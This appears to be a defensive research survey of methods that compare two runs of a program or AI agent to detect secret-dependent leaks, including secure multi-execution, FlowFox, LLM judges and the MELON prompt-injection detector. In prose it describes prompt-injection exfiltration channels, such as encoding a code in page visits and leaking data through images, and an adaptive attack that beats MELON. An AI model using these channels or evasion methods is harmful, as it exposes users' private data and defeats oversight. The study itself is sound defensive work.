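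If a program's code is available, an analyst can compare two runs without executing either. Barthe, D'Argenio and Rezk (2004), in *Secure information flow by self composition*, proposed joining two copies of the program, each with its own variables, and analysing the result as a single program. This is called self-composition. For an assistant that offers slot 11 only when the calendar contains an interview, the joined program is

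```
if reason1 = interview then offer1 := 11 else offer1 := 10
if reason2 = interview then offer2 := 11 else offer2 := 10
```

Both copies have the same free slots, but their reasons may differ. A checker searches for a pair of reasons that makes the offers differ. Here it finds an interview in one copy and an ordinary meeting in the other. If no such pair existed, the offer could not reveal the reason.

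Self-composition can be more precise than label rules. A type system, which checks labels in the program's text, rejects `output := secret; output := 0`, but self-composition accepts it because the final output is always 0. However, no algorithm can complete the self-composition check for every program.

Pandey and colleagues used self-composition to generate their pair of calendar runs automatically. Their tool, AL-SYNTH, takes two copies of a small hand-written model of the assistant and uses a solver to search for runs that agree on everything the assistant may use but differ in the offer. Nobody has a comparable description of how a language model chooses its actions. Li, Wang and colleagues (2026) point out in *PACE* that self-composition needs an adequate model of both runs, and that the code of an agent's tools doesn't show what the agent will pass to them. The operator of a real agent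 therefore has to produce the second run by running the language model again.

### A copy with the private data crossed out

*TightLip* (Yumerefendi, Mickle and Cox, 2007) compared two runs of ordinary Linux programs. When a program opens a sensitive file, the operating system starts a copy of the program. The original receives the real file, and the copy receives a version in the same format with the private content crossed out. The system then compares the requests the two programs make. If the requests and their arguments match, the output very probably doesn't depend on the private content. If they differ and the data is about to leave the computer, TightLip can block the transfer or let the copy take over from the original. A web server running on TightLip was only 5% slower.

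The comparison can miss a leak by chance. Suppose an outsider asks whether a secret number is even. If the secret number and its substitute are both even or both odd, the two runs give the same answer and TightLip detects nothing. With a random substitute, this would happen half the time, though longer answers rarely match by accident.

A bigger problem arises when the private content changes what the program does next. The two runs then do different things, so comparing them reveals little. From that point, TightLip has to treat everything the original run changes as secret, which causes the same false alarms as a cautious label tracker. Yumerefendi and colleagues therefore concentrated on programs such as file servers, which copy data without interpreting it. An agent interprets almost everything it reads, so its two runs would usually diverge early.

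### Secure multi-execution

*Noninterference Through Secure Multi-Execution* (Devriese and Piessens, 2010) also runs several copies, one for each secrecy level, but doesn't rely on comparing them. With two levels, the rules are:

1. The secret copy receives all the data. The public copy receives a fixed default value in place of each secret.
2. Only the public copy can write to public sinks. The secret copy can write only to places that may hold secrets.
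3. When the secret copy needs public input, it waits for the public copy to obtain it and reuses the result.

In one of their examples, a script in a webmail page reads the email that the user is writing and puts it into an image address on an outside server. The script also adds a 1 to the address if the email contains "abc" and a 0 if not, so the address contains both an explicit and an implicit flow. Under secure multi-execution, the public copy of the script requests the image but has a placeholder instead of the email. The server still receives a request, but the request no longer depends on what the user wrote.

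The same rules would stop an agent from spelling out the code 7294 through page visits. If the default code is 0000, the public copy requests page 0 four times, whatever the real code is. This works without anyone detecting a pattern in the visits, because the copy that makes them has never read the real code.

Devriese and Piessens proved that every program is noninterferent under these rules. If the scheduler also never makes the public copy wait for the secret one, the guarantee covers timing and whether the program finishes. They proved too that a program that was already secure in this strong sense produces the same output as before on every run that finishes. A monitor that only watches one run and halts it can't achieve both. *Transparent IFC Enforcement* (2020) explains that exact detection is impossible, so methods of this kind silently change the program's behaviour instead, and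 that all known ones run the program several times. (An operator who wants to know about attempted leaks can have the system issue a warning when the secret copy would have sent something different.)

On Google's JavaScript benchmarks, running the copies one after the other generally at least doubled the time but needed little extra memory. Running them in parallel on two processor cores took 2 to 25% longer than a normal run and used 50 to 100% more memory. A test with many simulated network delays ran faster than normal because the two copies could wait at the same time.

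### What FlowFox measured

*FlowFox* (De Groef, Devriese and colleagues, 2012) added secure multi-execution to Firefox. The modified browser runs two copies of each web script, one public and one secret, but performs each browser call only once. For example, a script might read the user's cookie (stored data that often keeps a user logged in), request an image, and arrange the page according to the image's width. The public copy requests the image without the real cookie, and the secret copy reuses the width that comes back.

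The team loaded the 500 most popular websites in two ordinary copies of Firefox and in FlowFox, which ran with a policy that made cookies secret. Advertisements and rotating pictures made pages differ even between the two ordinary copies, so the researchers ignored every pixel that differed there. In the remaining area, pages usually looked the same or almost the same in FlowFox as in Firefox. Scripts that tracked what users copied received empty text, and users saw no difference.

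Script benchmarks took roughly twice as long, but six realistic browsing tasks took only about 20% longer. Memory use rose by 88% on average. Comparing two runs of an agent would require a second series of model calls, which would roughly double its main running cost.

The websites worked well because they rarely need to send a secret to an outsider to function, whereas an agent often does. If a user asks an agent to tell a customer when a refund will arrive, a public copy that can't read the refund record can't write a correct reply. Rafnsson and Sabelfeld's *Secure Multi-Execution* extended the method to permit declassification, so an operator could release the refund date and withhold the rest of the record.

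### Nine models shown one run or two

Pandey and colleagues tested whether a language model can recognize a leak if it sees both runs. They wrote ten versions of the scheduling scenario and gave each to nine models three times. In one condition, the model judged the steps of the two runs one at a time, and in another it saw both runs together. The step-by-step condition also had two controls, a harmless case in which both runs offer the same slot and an obvious attack in which an injected instruction makes the agent forward data to an outsider.

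The table shows in how many of the 30 trials each judge objected.

| Judge | Leak, single steps | Harmless, single steps | Obvious attack, single steps | Leak, both runs together |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.8, GPT-5.5, Gemini 3.1 Pro, Grok 4.3, Qwen3.7-max and Qwen3-30B (each) | 0 | 0 | 30 | 30 |
| DeepSeek V4 Pro | 0 | 2 | 30 | 30 |
| Kimi K2.6 | 3 | 1 | 30 | 30 |
| Llama 4 Maverick | 0 | 0 | 30 | 17 |

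Eight of the nine judges never blocked the leak when they saw only single steps. Kimi's three objections probably reflect general caution, since it also objected to a harmless trial. All nine recognized the obvious attack every time, so they were not approving everything. Llama's 17 detections show that a judge can miss the difference between the two runs even when it is given both.

The perfect scores are weaker evidence than they look. The three repetitions measure how stable the answers are, so each score is based on only ten scenarios. A judge that misses a quarter of such leaks would still catch all ten about 6% of the time. Pandey and colleagues also report no trials with two harmless runs, so a judge that objected to every pair would also have scored 30.

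In the LangGraph version of the scenario, the comparison tool flagged the pair of runs that the per-action guard had allowed. The flag showed that the offer depended on the hidden reason, but not why. The cause could have been an attacker's instruction or an accident of how the agent chose between equally good slots.

### Coverage on paper

Pandey and colleagues also estimated which failures existing defences could catch. They divided failures into eight classes and credited each defence with everything its published design could observe.

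| Defence | Classes covered, out of 8 | Covers leaks visible only by comparing runs? |
|---|---|---|
| A person approves each tool call | 0 | No |
| Task Shield, which checks each action against the user's goal | 1 | No |
| RTBAS | 3 | No |
| CaMeL | 5 | No |
| FIDES | 7 | No |
| SAFEFLOW, another label-based system | 7 | No |
| Comparison of two runs | 8 | Yes |

A solver and an exhaustive search gave the same results for what each level of observation can detect in small models. This is good evidence about the models, but a flaw in a defence's code could reduce its real coverage.

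The last column also depends on how Pandey and colleagues treat false alarms. They give label systems credit for explicit flows, although label tracking causes some false alarms there. A cautious tracker would also stop the scheduling leak, but they count this as a failure because false alarms would be much more frequent. "No" therefore means that the defence can't distinguish the leak from ordinary work, though it may be able to block both.

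### Auditing Claude Sonnet 4.6

An agent that could leak information does not necessarily do so. Pandey and colleagues ran Claude Sonnet 4.6 as a scheduling assistant in 80 trials, keeping the free slots fixed and changing only the hidden reason. They also required that the assistant usually shared its availability, since an assistant that refuses to answer has no opportunity to leak.

They found no leaks. If each trial leaks with probability p, the chance of seeing none in n trials is (1 − p)ⁿ. Setting this to 5% gives the upper bound on p at 95% confidence:

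(1 − p)⁸⁰ = 0.05, so p ≈ 3.7%.

Lowering the bound to 1% would take 299 trials without a leak, and lowering it to 0.1% would take 2,995.

These figures assume that someone can recognize a leak in an individual trial. If the hidden reason only changes how often the assistant offers slot 11, the auditor has to compare frequencies instead. The next table extends the earlier calculation from a one-point change to larger changes, with the same test and 80% chance of detection.

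| How often the assistant offers slot 11 | Runs needed with each reason |
|---|---|
| 50% without an interview, 60% with one | about 390 |
| 50% without, 55% with | about 1,560 |
| 50% without, 51% with | about 39,000 |

Detecting a difference half as large takes about four times as many runs. Even with 80 runs for each reason, the test would miss the change from 50% to 60% about three times in four, so finding no difference is evidence only against large leaks.

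In an early analysis of the audit, the researchers reported a statistically significant leak, which persisted when they changed the random seeds. When they read the raw replies, they found that the assistant had offered the same slots in both conditions. Their software had counted a word that happened to differ between them. They treated this as a false positive because the purpose rule covers the slots, any stated reason and the recipient, but not the wording. However, if the wording varied systematically with the hidden reason, a recipient could learn the reason from it, and an auditor who ignored wording would miss that leak.

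### MELON: rerunning the agent without the user's task

*MELON* (Zhu, Yang and colleagues, 2025) also reruns the agent, but to detect injected instructions. The second run hides the user's task and leaves the secrets in place. If the agent proposes the same action without knowing the task, the action probably came from instructions in the data it has read. MELON therefore raises an alarm when the two runs match, whereas a test that replaces the secret raises one when they differ.

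Before each tool call, MELON does the following:

1. It gives the agent's model all the tool results so far, but replaces the user's request with a neutral instruction to summarise the content and carry out any instructions in it.
2. It stores the tool calls that the model proposes. It keeps them for the rest of the run, because the real agent may finish some of the user's work before it turns to the attacker's.
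3. It compares the real agent's next call with the stored ones by meaning, and stops the agent if any similarity exceeds 0.8.

Zhu and colleagues tested this on AgentDojo with GPT-4o and four styles of attack:

| | No defence | MELON |
|---|---|---|
| Successful attacks | 16.1% | 0.24% |
| Tasks completed under attack | 69.1% | 58.8% |
| Tasks completed without an attack | 80.4% | 68.0% |

The extra model calls roughly double the cost of using the model. MELON also raised false alarms in nine of the 97 harmless tasks. In all nine, the user had told the agent to carry out instructions from an outside source, such as a to-do list on a website. Zhu and colleagues consider such requests a real security risk. *APEX* (2026) concludes instead that replay measures what caused an action, not what the user authorized.

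*AgentVisor* (2026) reports a later test of MELON with the model GLM-4.7. Without an attack, MELON did not change how many tasks the agent completed. Under seven kinds of indirect attack, it kept the attack success rate at about 1% or below, but the share of tasks completed fell from 79–91% to 40–74%. One reason for such losses is that MELON ends the whole run when it detects an attack.

MELON's low attack rates also don't hold against an attacker who adapts. *The Attacker Moves Second* (2025) reports a 76% attack success rate against it with Llama 3.3 70B. Zhu and colleagues prove that taking a vote over many masked runs, each with a different neutral instruction, makes errors exponentially rarer. But the proof assumes that the runs err independently, and an attack that gets past one neutral instruction may well get past the others.

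### Which leaks a masked run can reveal

MELON would probably catch an injected instruction to send a key in four pieces. The agent in the masked run reads the same instruction and the same key, so it should propose similar requests, and MELON would stop the agent at the first match. Nobody appears to have tested this. MELON would not catch an agent copying credentials into a shared document at the user's request, because without that request, the agent in the masked run has no reason to write the document.

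It also examines only tool calls. Of 66 successful attacks that Zhu and colleagues studied, 48 worked through the text of the agent's reply, for example by persuading the user to buy something expensive. CamoLeak and EchoLeak both sent data out through images in the assistant's reply, which a check on tool calls would miss.

*AttriGuard* (2026) changes the tool results instead of the task. According to *DriftNet* (2026), it tests whether untrusted content caused a call by rerunning the agent on versions of those results that have less control over the agent. AttriGuard therefore runs the counterfactual that NeuroTaint predicts, but this requires control over the live agent. Neither MELON nor AttriGuard replaces the secret, so neither directly tests whether the agent's actions depend on it.

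### Runs that differ by chance

Li and colleagues note that comparing everything the agent sends out in two runs, with the secret replaced in one of them, covers encodings, paraphrases and fragments without a separate rule for each. This is a major advantage over searching for the secret, but a language model's outputs can differ between runs even when the secret stays the same.

Zhu and colleagues reduced the variation by setting the model's temperature, which controls its randomness, to zero and by counting similar calls as matches. Loose matching suits MELON because it makes an alarm more likely, but it would make one less likely in a test that replaces the secret. Requests for page 7 and page 2 are almost identical as text, so the test could treat them as equal and miss the changed digit. Exact matching would raise an alarm whenever the agent reworded an email.

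A control run shows how much variation is normal. De Groef and colleagues used a second ordinary Firefox as the control in their FlowFox test. *AgentSecBench* (Alpay and Alpay, 2026) pairs each attacked run with a harmless one and subtracts the rate at which the forbidden output appears in the harmless run. An auditor could run an agent twice with the same secret and once with a different one. But the auditor could not safely ignore everything that varies between the two same-secret runs, as the FlowFox test did with pixels, because the agent may leak the secret through how often it makes each choice.

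Secure multi-execution avoids this problem. The public copy may act at random, but its choices can't depend on the secret because it has no access to it. Devriese and Piessens's proof covers only deterministic programs, but they saw no fundamental obstacle to covering random ones.

### Sending the email once

A second run must not send a second email or make a second payment. MELON avoids this by comparing only one step ahead, recording the call that the masked run proposes without executing it. A longer comparison is harder because the second run needs a reply to its call before it can continue.

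TightLip makes the copy wait while the original program changes the system, then gives both the same result. Both also receive the same clock readings and network data, so only the redacted content can make them differ. This works until the two programs request different things. If an agent's second run emails a different person, there is no real reply to give it, and a simulated reply may lead the run to do things the real agent would not have done.

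Secure multi-execution carries out each public action once, through the public copy. The secret copy can reuse replies that the public copy requested but can't request others. Suppose a user has a confidential plan to buy a company and asks an agent to research the purchase. The secret copy reads the plan and needs the company's website. The public copy doesn't have the company's name, so it never opens the site, and the secret copy waits indefinitely. This protects the plan, because a visit could have revealed to the company that someone was interested. The agent could finish the research only if the user allowed it to reveal the company's name.
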